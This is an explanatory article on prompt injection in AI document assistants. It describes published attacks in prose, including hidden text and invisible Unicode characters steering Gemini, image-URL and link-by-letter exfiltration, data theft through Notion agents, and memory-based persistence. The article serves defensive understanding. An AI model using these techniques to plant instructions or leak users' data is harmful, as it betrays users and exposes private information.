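# Prompt injection in AI document and note tools: when it is harmless and when it is a security problem

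## How AI assistants read documents, and what prompt injection is

Prompt injection is text that makes a large language model, the kind of AI system behind ChatGPT, follow instructions that its user or developer did not intend. The text may come from the person typing into the chat box, or from a stranger who put it in a web page, email or PDF that the model processes later. Strangers' text has mattered more since software companies built language models into the tools where people keep their work. Notion, Slack, Confluence, Google Workspace and Microsoft 365 each now have a document assistant, an AI feature that reads the user's pages, files, mail or messages and writes summaries, answers and sometimes edits. Much of the text these assistants read was written by other people, and the user may never have looked at it.

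### One request, from start to finish

Suppose an employee opens a document assistant and types "summarize this report". The request goes through roughly the same steps in every document assistant.

The tool first gathers text. If the report is already open, there is little to find. If the request is vaguer, the tool searches the workspace. In Notion, according to its security documentation, the model turns the request into a search query. The query runs against an index in which each page has an embedding, a list of numbers that represents the page's meaning, so pages on similar subjects have similar embeddings. Software then ranks the best matches. This step is generally called retrieval. Microsoft calls it grounding and lists emails, chats, meetings, files, attachments and the public web among the sources that its assistant, Copilot, can draw on.

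Next the tool assembles the context, which is all the text the model receives for this request. The context contains the developer's instructions (the "system prompt", which users normally do not see), the employee's request, and the report, along with anything else that was retrieved. Slack, for example, describes building an assistant that summarizes a channel by sending the model one prompt containing both the messages and the instructions for summarizing them.

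The model writes its answer from that context one token (a word or part of a word) at a time. The tool usually formats the answer and shows it to the user, but it may also act on it. For example, Microsoft lists "command generation" among the steps between the model's response and the user's screen, and Notion advertises agents that organize a workspace and carry out tasks in it. An agent adds the result of each action to the context and runs the model again, so a single request can bring in new text many times.

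All three companies limit the assistant to material the user is already allowed to see. Microsoft, for instance, ties Copilot's access to the permissions of the signed-in user. This keeps an intern's assistant from reading the payroll file, but it doesn't restrict who wrote the material the assistant reads. The assistant can read a stranger's email in an employee's inbox because the employee is allowed to read it.

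### Why the model cannot reliably tell an instruction from data

The programmer Simon Willison gives the standard illustration in *Prompt injection* (2023), using a small translation program built on GPT-3, an early OpenAI model. In the first part of the prompt, the developer instructed the model to translate whatever followed into French and return the result in a fixed data format. Instead of text to translate, Willison entered a request for the language of an eighteenth-century pirate, along with a sentence about a security hole. The model returned the sentence in pirate English, in the data format the developer had specified.

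The program had joined two pieces of text and the model had continued the result, so nothing had malfunctioned in the usual sense. In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, a December 2025 article for Britain's National Cyber Security Centre, David C explains that a model predicts the most likely next token from all the text so far, and that nothing in this operation separates instructions from material to be processed.

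Developers have tried to mark where each part of the text comes from. GPT-4 had a separate slot for the developer's instructions, but Willison still got it to talk like a pirate by typing text formatted to look like new developer instructions. Later models label every part of the context with a role, such as "user" for the person asking and "tool" for a fetched web page, and are trained to prioritize some roles over others.

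Ye, Cui and Hadfield-Menell (2026), in *Prompt Injection as Role Confusion*, tested whether those labels determine which role the model internally assigns to text. They wrapped identical passages of ordinary web text in each role label in turn and trained a simple classifier to recover the role from the model's internal activity. Because the wording never changed, the classifier could learn only from the labels' effect on that activity. They then ran it on a short conversation about gardening. The passages in which the model had reasoned to itself scored 85 percent as "reasoning" with correct labels and 83 percent with no labels. They scored 85 percent again when the researchers labeled the whole conversation as user text, which shows that the style of the passages had outweighed their label.

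The same measurement predicted how often attacks succeeded. Across 1,000 attempts to make an agent leak data, the attack success rate (the share of attempts that achieve the attacker's goal) rose from 2 percent where the classifier measured the least confusion about roles to 70 percent where it measured the most. But when the researchers hid a simple fake command in a web page, all but one of the models they tested obeyed it no more than 2 percent of the time. Ye and colleagues attribute that resistance to familiarity with known attacks, but we cannot tell from a low success rate alone whether they are right.

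Prompt injection can happen without an attacker. *Accidental prompt injection against RAG applications* (Willison, 2024) describes a demo that a developer built to answer questions from the documentation for Willison's own software. Answering from retrieved text is called retrieval-augmented generation, or RAG. When the developer asked the demo for the meaning of life, it replied in the character of a witty gerbil. The documentation had nothing on the meaning of life, but embedding search ranks pages by similarity and always returns something. The nearest match was a set of release notes with a sample command telling a model to play a gerbil.

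### The name, and the comparison with SQL injection

On September 11, 2022, Riley Goodside posted examples on Twitter in which GPT-3 was asked to translate a sentence but obeyed a command inside it. The next day, Willison (2022) proposed the name "prompt injection" in *Prompt injection attacks against GPT-3*. According to a Wikipedia article that PrivacyTools mirrors, Jonathan Cefalu of the company Preamble had already reported the flaw to OpenAI that May as "command injection".

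Willison took the name from SQL injection, a well-known website vulnerability. SQL is a language programs use to query databases. If a program builds a query by pasting a visitor's username into a line of SQL, a malicious visitor can enter a "username" that closes the quotation early and adds a command, such as one that deletes a table of customers. The database then runs that command. Parameterized queries prevent this by sending the command and the username separately, so the database never treats the username as a command.

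In this comparison, the problem is that trusted and untrusted text are combined in one string. Willison hoped for a way to give GPT-3 the instructions and the data separately. In April 2023 he added a note to the post saying that this now looked extremely difficult, if not impossible, given the way language models were then designed.

NIST (2025), the US standards agency, still compares the lack of separate channels for data and instructions to the flaw behind SQL injection. David C considers the parallel dangerous because it leads engineers to expect an equally complete fix. He prefers an older idea, the confused deputy, in which someone who lacks access tricks a program that has it into acting on their behalf. Programmers can usually fix a confused deputy, but David C calls language models "inherently confusable". The two views are compatible, since NIST is describing the cause of the problem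 and David C is discussing how fully it can be fixed.

### Direct injection, indirect injection and jailbreaking

In direct injection, the person using the assistant types the injected text. In indirect injection, an outsider places it in content that the assistant reads later, and the consequences usually fall on someone other than that outsider. Greshake, Endres and colleagues introduced indirect injection in *Not what you've signed up for* (2023) and classified the ways it can arrive. An attacker can leave the text on a public page for a search to find, email it to the victim, or add it to a passage that a reader copies from a website and pastes into a chatbot. The last case is still indirect because an outsider wrote the injected text, even though the user pasted it.

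In March 2024, Willison distinguished jailbreaking, which tries to defeat the safety rules a company has trained into a model, from prompt injection, which attacks an application that mixes trusted and untrusted text. An employee who coaxes an assistant into explaining how to make a weapon is jailbreaking it. If the employee tricks it into printing its developer's instructions, that is direct injection. If a supplier sends an invoice containing text that makes a customer's assistant forward the customer's mail, that is indirect injection.

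Writers do not keep to these boundaries, so they often talk past one another. Ho's Microsoft article, *Safeguarding AI against 'jailbreaks' and other prompt attacks*, uses "jailbreak" for any direct attack. NIST treats jailbreaking as one type of direct attack. OpenAI's *Understanding prompt injections* (2025) reserves "prompt injection" for text from a third party, which excludes direct attacks, and Google's help page for Gemini in Workspace covers both. Whether a writer calls "prompt injection" trivial or grave may depend on which meaning they have in mind.

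### Text that the model receives and the reader does not see

Injected text can be in plain view. Microsoft (2025), describing its defenses against indirect injection, notes that a plain text file can carry an injection, and few people read to the end of a long report before asking for a summary. Hiding the text still helps the attacker, and it is easy because the person and the model receive different versions of the document. The person sees what Word or a PDF viewer draws on the screen, while the assistant usually gets text that a program called an extractor has pulled from the file. Li (2026), in *When File Ingestion Misleads Language Models*, estimates that extraction costs about a hundredth as much as having a model process images of the pages, which explains why most products rely on it.

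The simplest way to hide text is to make it white on a white page. A reader can't see it, but an extractor reads it like any other text. Willison reports that Mark Riedl, an academic, put a line of white text on his profile page, and Microsoft's Bing began describing him as an expert on time travel. *PhantomLint* (2025) lists other methods for PDFs, including tiny or fully transparent letters, text underneath another object, and text outside the visible area of the page. Unicode, the standard that gives every character a number, also includes invisible characters, and a string of them can reach the model without appearing on screen.

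Office files can hold text in many more places, including comments, speaker notes, hidden rows, image descriptions and metadata (information about the file, such as its title and properties). Li examined ten widely used extractors for Word, Excel and PowerPoint and found 19 kinds of location where at least one extractor passed on text that a reader would not see, and 12 where at least one dropped text that a reader would see. Li's own attacks contained no instructions, so Li classes them as misinformation rather than prompt injection. For example, a spreadsheet cell can store 1,000,000 while its number format displays $1,000. This kind of trick misled ChatGPT, Claude, Gemini and Microsoft 365 Copilot in at least nine of ten trials each.

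Most hidden text probably has an innocent purpose. *Who Is Prompt-Injecting Coding Agents?* (2026) found hidden text in 3.4 percent of 142.7 million issues, pull requests and comments on GitHub, the site where programmers share code. Nearly all of it was in HTML comments, a standard place for notes that a web page does not display.

### What can follow

The possible consequences, in roughly rising order of seriousness, are these:

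1. Odd output: the assistant answers like a pirate or a gerbil.
2. Prompt leak: the assistant reveals the hidden instructions its developer wrote.
3. Misleading output: a summary omits a warning, or a recommendation favors whoever planted the text.
4. Altered documents: the assistant writes false or unwanted content into the user's own files.
5. Lasting changes to memory: the assistant stores a planted preference and applies it in later conversations.
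6. Data theft: private text reaches someone outside.
7. Unauthorized actions: the assistant sends mail, deletes files or runs commands in the user's name.

The order is a rule of thumb, since a misleading summary of a contract could do more harm than the theft of a lunch invitation. Some cases are also closer to pushy marketing than to crime. For example, Microsoft found 31 companies using "Summarize with AI" buttons to plant favorable mentions of themselves in assistants' memories.

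Security engineers sort such harms by what they damage. Integrity means that nobody has wrongly altered data or the output people rely on. Misleading summaries, altered documents and planted memories all violate it. Confidentiality means that nobody has wrongly disclosed data. Data theft violates it, and a prompt leak is a minor violation. An unauthorized action can violate either one.

To steal data, an attacker needs both a misled model and an outward channel, meaning any feature through which data can leave the tool. Moving private data through such a channel to a place the attacker controls is called exfiltration. Microsoft describes several channels. The assistant's answer may include an image whose web address points to the attacker's server and ends with private text, which the user's browser sends to that server when it tries to load the image. Such an attack can be zero-click, meaning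 that the victim need not open, click or approve anything the attacker sent. A link can send out data in the same way, but the user must click it. A tool that sends email or posts to a public site can send the data out directly. Willison calls the combination of private data, untrusted content and an outward channel in one system the "lethal trifecta".

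## The case that prompt injection in these tools is harmless

### Two hours with Notion AI

Notion announced its document assistant, Notion AI, in November 2022. Its early features drafted essays, continued paragraphs, listed pros and cons, or picked out the action items on a page. Each took in text and returned text to the user. In December, Shawn Wang, a developer and writer known online as swyx, got access to this early version and within two hours had extracted what appeared to be the hidden instructions behind every feature. He published them in Latent Space's *Reverse Prompt Engineering for Fun and (no) Profit* to show that there was "nothing to fear".

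When he asked the model directly for its instructions, he got only a paraphrase. He came closer to the wording by asking the model to translate the instructions from English into English. That didn't work for some features, so he guessed how their instructions began, based on the ones he already had, and asked the model for the rest. He also watched the traffic between the Notion app and its servers and saw that the feature for continuing a paragraph used the page's title and the text around the cursor.

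The results were unremarkable. The instructions for "Help me write" described the model as an assistant helping a user write, specified a format and prohibited links.

The instructions Wang published may not have been quite the real ones. A Notion employee replied on Hacker News that some of the text was verbatim and some reordered, that the model had invented some of it, and that "a bunch is missing". Wang printed the reply and conceded in a footnote that he had only "an educated guess" at the prompts. A model asked for hidden text can invent some of it, and an outsider has no original to check it against. This does little to weaken Wang's argument, which is that the prompts are worth very little to whoever gets them. He thought a junior developer could build a working copy of Notion AI from what he had published, and that someone with no technical training could write ten alternatives in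 an afternoon.

### Takeovers, leaks and client-side JavaScript

Wang divided the results of prompt injection into two kinds. In a "prompt takeover", the product outputs text its developer did not intend, as when Willison's translation program responded like a pirate. Wang thought takeovers were embarrassing but mostly a risk to reputation, since people generally have to seek out the bad output. A "prompt leak", which reveals the developer's prompt, looked more serious because companies building on the same model might consider their prompts valuable intellectual property. So he leaked the prompts of a company worth $10 billion and challenged his readers to name the worst that could happen.

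Wang compared prompts to client-side JavaScript, the code that a website sends to each visitor's browser. Anyone can read that code, so competent developers keep passwords out of it and have the server check every request, whatever the code in the browser does. Wang argued that prompts are likewise a part of the product that anyone can reverse engineer, and that they expose a company to attack to exactly the same degree. Notion had put its assistant behind the same login and security checks as the rest of its service, and he thought it needed no other protection.

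The comparison works only if developers treat prompts the way they treat browser code. Suppose a developer writes "do not show salaries to interns" into a prompt and relies on the model to follow it. An intern who gets around that instruction can read the salaries, and the developer is at fault for not making the server refuse the request.

Willison quoted the comparison on his blog that December. The following April, he warned developers that they were taking prompt injection too lightly, but he accepted Wang's case as it applied to the product Wang had tested. He advised developers to assume their prompts would leak, to treat them as "effectively public data" and not to waste time hiding them. He also agreed that if an application shows its output only to the person who sent the text, "it's not a crisis" when that person tricks it into doing something weird.

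### The four premises

Wang does not set out his argument in steps, but it rests on four premises:

1. The attacker is the user: whoever writes the injection is also the person using the assistant.
2. The output goes back only to that user.
3. The assistant has no further powers. It can return text and do nothing else.
4. Ordinary access controls, such as logins and page permissions, guard the data.

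If all four conditions hold, an employee who gets the assistant to misbehave has not been deceived, because they wanted the odd result. Nobody else sees it unless the employee shares it. The assistant cannot delete pages or send emails, and it can only use pages the employee could already open. Only Notion could still be harmed, by the disclosure of some unremarkable instructions and perhaps slight embarrassment.

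The argument is strong because it doesn't depend on how often people attempt prompt injection or how well the model resists it. Under these conditions, a model would be safe even if it obeyed every injection.

Wang stated the second premise when he wrote that takeovers do mainly reputational damage "as long as the output is solely contained in response to the prompter". He made exceptions for output that someone publishes without context and output that affects what the general public later sees. He also called prompt injection only "probably" harmless. The fourth premise appears in his praise for Notion's security checks. He left the first and third unstated, presumably because nothing in his test challenged them.

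Jonathan Cefalu, whose company Preamble had reported the flaw to OpenAI earlier that year, gave two counterexamples in a comment on the Latent Space post. In one, a company uses a language model to screen messages for harmful content, and an attacker writes a message that gets the model to mark it as harmless. The second premise fails here because the model's verdict decides what other people see. In the other, a brand offers free pictures of its mascot, and someone bypasses the instructions and generates whatever pictures they like. All four premises can hold in this case, but the brand still pays for the pictures. So the argument shows at most that prompt injection is harmless to everyone except the developer, and the developer's loss is usually small.

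The first premise was weaker than it looked, even in 2022. Wang had found that some Notion AI features read the page as well as the user's request, and he tried putting injections in page titles. He used his own pages, but on a page written by a client or colleague, the same features would have read that person's text. Two months later, Greshake and colleagues pointed out that work on prompt injection had so far assumed that the user was prompting the model, and they asked what would happen if someone else was.

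### When an outsider writes the text

Once companies had connected assistants to mail and shared files, nobody could rely on the first premise. The modified argument is that even if an outsider wrote the text, the assistant still only shows the user an answer, and the user decides what to do about it. Anyone who can email a person can already lie to that person. On this view, an assistant that repeats the lie adds little to the problem of phishing, in which a fraudulent message tricks someone into giving up a password or money.

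Google's handling of a 2024 report fits this view. In *New Gemini for Workspace Vulnerability Enabling Phishing & Content Manipulation*, Martin and Yeung (2024) describe testing Google's assistant, Gemini, for the AI security company HiddenLayer. They first emailed themselves an injection that made Gemini greet the user by a silly name, cluck like a chicken and recite a poem instead of describing the email. They called this amusing but not dangerous. They then hid the injection in white text. When they asked about the email, Gemini warned them of a compromised password and directed them to a web address that resembled Google's.

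Martin and Yeung put an injection in the speaker notes of a Google Slides presentation. Gemini automatically summarizes a presentation when a user opens the sidebar, so opening it was enough to make Gemini write a poem based on the title of a 1980s pop song.

In Google Drive, they stored a rant about bananas in one file and an injection in another, then asked Gemini to summarize the rant. Gemini returned the output the injection called for. When they shared the injected file from a different account, Gemini did not at first mistake it for the banana document, but once they mentioned bananas in its title, Gemini retrieved it and followed the injection. An outsider could therefore get instructions to a user's assistant by sharing a file with a suitable name.

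Martin and Yeung demonstrated that the behavior was possible in three products but gave no success rates. Google marked the Gmail report "Won't Fix (Intended Behavior)" and told them it already knew about the Slides behavior and considered that intended too.

Martin and Yeung record no further explanation from Google. The label makes some sense, since an assistant that summarizes email has to repeat what strangers write. But a faithful summary would have attributed the password warning to the email. Gemini presented the warning as its own and left out the rest of the email. Martin and Yeung concluded that an outsider could make Gemini "display whatever message they want", which cast doubt on its reliability. They did not show that any data had left the account or that Gemini had taken any action. They advised users to stay vigilant, and the modified dismissal also depends on users doing so.

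Google has since changed its approach. *Mitigating prompt injection attacks*, a Google post from June 2025, describes injected emails, documents and calendar invitations as a threat that needs "immediate attention". By then Google had trained its Gemini 2.5 models on examples of such attacks and added other defenses, including software that looks for injections and a step that removes suspicious web addresses. A month later, Security Boulevard's *Google Gemini AI Flaw Could Lead to Gmail Compromise, Phishing* (2025) reported that hidden text in an email could still put a fake security alert into Gemini's summary.

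Gemini now checks the files a user asks about for suspicious prompts and links. According to Google's help page, it blocks the request or leaves out the suspect material, and notifies the user. Google is therefore trying to prevent what it called intended behavior in 2024, but it does not promise to succeed. In *Google Workspace’s continuous approach to mitigating indirect prompt injections*, Gavish (2026) writes for Google's security team that indirect prompt injection is not a problem "you 'solve' and move on".

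### Google's decision on invisible characters

Google stated its reasons more fully in 2025, in response to a report about invisible text. Unicode includes a block of invisible "tag" characters that duplicates the ordinary English letters, digits and punctuation. The block was meant for marking a text's language and is now largely obsolete (Microsoft, 2026). Security researchers call writing a hidden message in these characters "ASCII smuggling", after ASCII, the older character set that the block copies.

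Viktor Markopoulos of the security company FireTail tried hiding text in calendar invitations. *ASCII Smuggling in Google Gemini*, which Markopoulos wrote as vict0ni, describes an event whose title appeared in the calendar as "Meeting" but which Gemini read to the invited user as "Meeting. It is optional." Hidden text could also replace the description, the meeting link and the organizer's name, and one test invitation purported to come from Barack Obama. Gemini would read an invitation even if the user had not accepted it.

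FireTail reported this to Google on September 18, 2025, received what Cyber Security News calls a "no action" response, and published its findings. In its reply, quoted in BGR's *Google Has No Plans To Fix This Terrifying Gemini Security Vulnerability*, Google argued that the attack "can only result in social engineering", meaning tricking a person instead of breaking into a system, and that a fix "would not make our users less prone to such attacks".

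The first reason accurately describes the calendar test, in which Gemini misreported a meeting and did nothing else. FireTail replied that the risk changes once an assistant can access an inbox. Tom's Guide's *Researcher finds security flaw in Gemini* quotes the researchers as saying that hidden commands in an email could tell an assistant to search for sensitive items and send out contact details. The calendar test did not demonstrate this, so FireTail's reply to Google was a prediction.

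Evidence from another Google product supports the prediction. In August 2025 the security researcher Johann Rehberger showed that Jules, Google's Gemini-based coding agent, would follow invisible text in a task description and add and run code that the user had not asked for. According to Embrace The Red's *Google Jules is Vulnerable To Invisible Prompt Injection*, Rehberger had reported the underlying behavior in February 2024, and Google had accepted it as a valid bug. Social engineering was the worst outcome in the calendar test because of what Gemini could do there, not because of any limit on what invisible characters can instruct a model to do.

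Google's second reason is harder to dismiss. An attacker who can no longer use invisible characters can still put a lie in the visible text of a calendar invitation, and some people will believe it. But the user or a spam filter would at least have a chance to notice it.

The fix also looks easy. FireTail found that ChatGPT, Copilot and Claude resisted the technique, apparently by removing the characters, while Gemini, Grok and DeepSeek did not. Microsoft found only one routine use of the characters in legitimate email, in the flag emojis of England, Scotland and Wales. It advises stripping or normalizing the characters before an assistant reads a message.

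In February 2026, Embrace The Red's *Scary Agent Skills* still listed Gemini among the models known to treat tag characters as instructions. It also listed Claude, despite FireTail's earlier result. Rehberger had got Claude Code, Anthropic's coding tool, to obey such text, but when he tried again on February 10, it consistently detected the characters and refused. He found no such protection in the Claude web app for the same kind of file. Whether the hidden instructions work evidently depends on the product as well as the model, and these findings are too old to show how Gemini behaves at the end of 2026.

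### Which features removed which premise

The first premise no longer holds in shared documents, because the person who wrote the text may not be the person using the assistant. The second also fails if the assistant writes its answer into a page that a whole team uses, because the output then reaches people who didn't ask for it and may not know that a model wrote it.

With retrieval, the user no longer chooses what the assistant reads. Someone who asks for a summary of an open page knows which page the assistant will read, but a tool that searches a whole drive or mailbox may pick a file the user has never opened. Retrieval also weakens the fourth premise. The access controls still work as designed, but they do not restrict who wrote a file, so if an outsider wrote it, the assistant handles that text with all of the user's access.

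Web access extended the first problem to anyone who can publish a page. It also undermined the second and third premises, because a tool that requests web addresses can also send information out. Writer, a company that sells an AI writing tool, told researchers that a data leak they had reported was not a security issue, arguing that customers' accounts had no access to any website. Willison called the reply "a huge failure".

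The third premise does not hold for agents. In April 2023 Willison had already written that prompt injection "turns from a curiosity to a genuinely dangerous vulnerability" when a model can use tools. Agents also weaken the modified dismissal, which relies on the user to judge the result, because an agent can act on an answer and do harm before the user has judged it. Gavish notes that an indirect injection may work without any input from the user. Wang had good reason to call Notion's first assistant harmless, but Notion now offers agents that carry out tasks across a workspace.

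## The case that it is a security flaw

### From curiosity to vulnerability

In April 2023, responding to people who doubted that prompt injection was serious, Willison pointed to a voice assistant that the developer Justin Alvey had built to search his email and send replies he dictated. Willison asked what the assistant would do if an incoming email contained instructions to forward several recent emails to a stranger and then delete them. The assistant put the text of emails into the model's context, and by default nothing would have stopped the model from following those instructions.

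That example was hypothetical, but Willison also ran a demonstration with plugins, which at the time let ChatGPT call outside services. His own plugin let ChatGPT query a database. He told ChatGPT to look up user records and produce a web address containing them, and it did. Willison typed the instruction himself, but a stranger could have emailed it to anyone who had installed both his plugin and one for reading email.

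Shawn Wang had examined a single product with a fixed set of features. Willison worried most about the growing number of plugin combinations. A plugin that reads mail and one that queries a database may each pass inspection, and the danger appears only when a user installs both.

### The confused deputy

Later that month, *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants* (Willison, 2023) described the most dangerous form of prompt injection as a confused deputy attack, an idea decades older than language models. Norm Hardy's *The Confused Deputy* tells a "nearly true story" about Tymshare, a company that rented out time on its computers. Tymshare's compiler, which turned customers' source code into runnable programs, let each customer name a file for debugging output.

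*The Confused Deputy*, a set of lecture slides from UT Austin, describes an attack that used a compiler with permission to update a billing file that customers could not change. A customer named that file as the destination for the compiler's debugging output. The operating system confirmed that the compiler could write there and let it overwrite the bills.

The access check had worked as designed. The compiler had authority from both the system and the customer, and it used the system's authority to carry out the customer's request. A document assistant that reads a stranger's text is in a similar position. If hidden text in a supplier's PDF leads the assistant to open a payroll page, the server will allow it because the employee has permission to open that page.

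The episode convinced Hardy that operating systems need capabilities, which are tokens that identify a resource and carry permission to use it. With capabilities, a customer who had no token for the billing file could not have directed the compiler to it. A sentence in a PDF comes with no such token, so the model can only infer whose instruction it is.

The usual stopgap is to ask the user before the assistant acts. Willison predicted in 2023 that users would learn to click "OK" as fast as possible. In *30 posts tagged "lethal-trifecta"*, he reports that Anthropic later tested this with 1,053 paid testers of its coding tool. Partway through each session, the researchers replaced one permission request with a clearly dangerous command, and only 13.6 percent of the testers refused it. People may read a request to send an email more carefully than a line of code, but the result still weakens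 the argument that users will stop a misled model from doing harm.

### Why no parameterized query exists for English

David C, writing for Britain's National Cyber Security Centre, explains why he expects the problem to last. He starts with SQL injection and two other old vulnerabilities, all of which involve a machine treating data as instructions. In cross-site scripting, an attacker's text runs as code in another visitor's browser. In a buffer overflow, overlong input spills into memory that the program uses for something else.

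Instructions are clearly defined in those machines, so engineers can build a boundary that the machine enforces. Parameterized queries do this for databases, and some ARM processors tag regions of memory with their purpose. A language model has no such definition for engineers to enforce. Developers can scan for injections, train the model to prefer some instructions, or mark which passages are data, but David C objects that each of these imposes a distinction that the underlying technology lacks. Ye and colleagues' experiments on role labels support his objection.

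He writes that there is "a good chance" that nobody will ever fully fix prompt injection, which is weaker than saying that nobody can. The argument shows that a developer cannot promise that attacks will fail, but not that they often succeed.

David C therefore advises developers to assume that an attacker who controls some of the model's input could use any tool the model can use, and to limit the tools accordingly. He recommends a rule from an exchange between Willison and Baibhav Bista: a model that reads someone's text should temporarily drop to that person's privileges. An assistant reading a supplier's invoice could then do only what the supplier could do. That would be safe, but it would rule out much of what companies now advertise, such as an agent that reads incoming mail and updates the company's records. David C thinks a system that cannot tolerate the remaining risk may be a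 poor use for a language model.

Other specialists still described the problem in similar terms in 2026. At a security conference in June, Ariel Fogel of OWASP, which publishes widely used lists of software risks, called prompt injection an "unresolved problem" in the architecture of generative AI (Poireault, 2026, *Prompt Injection Remains Unsolved, OWASP Researcher Warns*). In July, Constantin (2026) reported in *AI agent security* that four research teams had broken AI agents in four ways within ten days. The targets included Anthropic's browser agent and agents' stored memories, and Constantin traced all four attacks to the same flaw.

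### The lethal trifecta

Willison (2025), in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, argues that an attacker can steal data through any assistant that can access private data, reads untrusted content and can send information out. Private data includes the assistant's memories of earlier conversations as well as mail and files. An inbox counts as untrusted content because anyone can send email to it.

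An attacker can use prompt injection to steal data only if the assistant has access to private data, reads untrusted content that can carry the attacker's instructions, and can send data out. Willison recommends removing the ability to send data out, because an assistant that can't read the user's files or incoming mail isn't much use.

Web access can meet two of the conditions at once, because a page the assistant opens may contain hostile text, and the address it requests can carry private text to the attacker's server. A workspace assistant already has private data, so turning on web access may be enough to meet all the conditions.

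Anthropic had anticipated this and restricted its chat assistant, Claude, to addresses that the user had typed or that its search tool had returned, so an attacker could not just have it add private text to an address. But Claude could also follow links on pages it had already opened, and in July 2026 Willison described how Ayush Paul used this to get around the restriction. Paul built a site with a link for each letter of the alphabet and text instructing AI assistants to find the user's profile by spelling out the user's name. Claude followed the links one letter at a time, and the server recorded the order, which gave Paul the user's name, home city and employer. Anthropic has since stopped Claude from following links found on pages it fetches.

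Vendors' repairs also fit Willison's account. By June 2025 he had listed 14 cases of data theft through AI products, including Slack, Google's NotebookLM and Microsoft Copilot. Almost all the vendors had fixed them promptly, usually by blocking the route by which data left the product. The model could still follow a stranger's instructions, but it could no longer send data out by that route.

Closing a channel properly can be hard. Salesforce, the customer-management software company, had limited its agent to images from approved domains. One of those domains had expired, so researchers registered it and had the agent send them sales contacts. Combining tools can also reopen a channel that each vendor has closed in its own product. Willison doesn't think it's reasonable to expect ordinary users to notice this.

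### One supplier's PDF in five configurations

Suppose a supplier sends a price list as a PDF that contains a hidden instruction to AI assistants. An employee saves the PDF in a note tool and asks the tool's assistant for help with an order. Assume that the model follows every instruction in its input, to separate the tool's effect from the model's. Each row of the table adds a feature to the tool in the row above.

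| What the assistant can do | What the attacker gains | Premise of the harmless view that fails |
|---|---|---|
| Read only the employee's own text | Nothing, because the PDF's text never reaches the model | None |
| Read the PDF and answer in plain text | Control over the answer, which can omit a price increase or give a false warning | The attacker is the user |
| Add the employee's other private pages to the context | A more convincing lie, which can mention real budgets and names; the attacker sees none of this unless the employee passes it on | Ordinary access controls guard the data: they still work, but they no longer keep a stranger's instructions away from private text |
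| Display images and links | The private text itself, through an image as soon as the answer appears or through a link if the employee clicks it | The output goes back only to the user |
| Search the web and send email | Theft with nothing visible in the answer, and the power to send messages in the employee's name | The assistant has no further powers |

The theft becomes possible when the tool begins displaying images and links, a change few people would think of as a security decision. The PDF, the model and the private pages stay the same, and the employee may see no difference in the answer.

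Willison's April 2023 rules allow a model to mix untrusted text with private data if it can produce no outbound links or images and uses only services that will not leak data. *A Lifecycle and Application-Stack Survey of Large Language Model Vulnerabilities* (2026) is stricter, treating any deployment that mixes untrusted content with instructions and private data as high risk unless the developer adds strong controls. By that standard, the assistant is high risk once it can read the private pages, even if it has no way to send data out.

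The stricter standard has some merit. Willison himself describes how a model could persuade a user to copy scrambled private text and paste it into a stranger's website. A tool that can't send data out may also gain that ability in its next update. But until it does, a thief needs the employee's help, so "high risk" seems too strong unless the private data is especially sensitive.

### Schneier on Notion's agents

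In September 2025, just after Notion released version 3.0, a researcher showed that hidden text in a PDF could make a Notion agent send out a client list through its web search. In *Abusing Notion's AI Agent for Data Theft*, security technologist Bruce Schneier wrote, "We have zero agentic AI systems that are secure against these attacks." He thought most developers were pretending the problem didn't exist, and that Notion was no worse than the rest. He also described himself as basically an optimist about AI.

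Wang and Schneier reached opposite conclusions about Notion, but Wang was judging its 2022 writing aid, while Schneier was judging an agent that could read a company's records and search the web. Schneier also used a demanding standard, counting a system as secure only if it stays safe when someone is deliberately trying to break it.

The best evidence against his "zero" is from August 2026 and concerns a coding agent, Claude Code. Anthropic commissioned Trajectory Labs to try 72 indirect injection scenarios on it, and none of 720 attempts succeeded against three recent Claude models running in the tool's automatic mode.

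Willison wrote that he would love to believe it but wanted more independent confirmation. He described an attack that he thought no version of the automatic mode could stop, in which a project's test instructions include downloading a package that turns out to steal data. Developers download and run packages every day, so the request looks normal. Even if the attempts were statistically independent, 720 failed attempts would also be compatible with a true success rate of up to about 0.4 percent.

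### The promptware kill chain

Schneier is also one of the four researchers behind a more detailed version of the argument. Brodt, Feldman and colleagues (2026), in *The Promptware Kill Chain*, argue that the term "prompt injection" now understates the attacks it covers, because it describes only how they begin. They call the attacks "promptware", meaning malicious software that consists of prompts, and divide them into seven stages. (A kill chain is a security term for the steps of an attack.)

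1. Initial access: the attacker's text enters the model's context.
2. Privilege escalation: the text jailbreaks the model, which here includes getting it past its developer's instructions.
3. Reconnaissance: the model finds out which files and tools it can reach.
4. Persistence: the instructions survive the conversation.
5. Command and control: the assistant keeps fetching new instructions from the attacker.
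6. Lateral movement: the attack spreads to other users, programs or agents.
7. Actions on objective: the attacker gets what they wanted, such as data or money.

Attacks may skip or combine stages. Two forms of persistence matter for document tools. An injected page can stay in a workspace and take effect whenever someone's question leads a search to retrieve it. If the attacker gets an instruction into the assistant's long-term memory, it applies to every later conversation.

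In October 2024 Johann Rehberger used ChatGPT's memory for command and control by getting the assistant to remember to check a GitHub page for new commands. Morris II, a March 2024 demonstration against email assistants, showed lateral movement. An incoming message stayed in the victim's mail database, and the assistant later retrieved it and copied the injection into outgoing mail, where it could reach other people's assistants.

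Brodt and colleagues then classified 36 prominent studies and incidents by the number of stages each covered. None of the three from 2023 covered four or more stages, but seven of the 12 from 2024 did, as did 15 of the 21 from 2025 and January 2026. None of the 36 covered more than five.

The apparent steep rise is weak evidence of what attackers are doing, because the researchers chose the cases, many were demonstrations, and three cases are a small base for a trend. The definition of persistence is also broad. An injected Slack message counts as persistent because it stays in the workspace until someone's question retrieves it, which is true of almost any message.

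The number of stages is also a poor measure of the damage. A January 2026 attack on Notion AI had only three: an uploaded document carried the injection, the injection got past the product's controls, and personnel data leaked. Leaked salary data harms a company even when the attack involves no lateral movement.

The kill chain is more useful for deciding what to repair. A company may remove a malicious PDF and believe it has ended the attack while an instruction from the PDF remains in the assistant's memory. Brodt and colleagues found far more published defenses against the first two stages than against the later ones, and none against reconnaissance. They also concede part of Wang's point. An application that is open to injection but has no persistence, no way to spread and no powerful actions is at lower risk than one that allows all seven stages.

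### Harm without theft

David C illustrates prompt injection with a recruiter who uses a model to judge whether CVs meet a job's requirements. One candidate's CV contains hidden text instructing the model to approve it. If the model complies, the wrong person may get an interview, but the trifecta does not cover this case because no private data has left the company.

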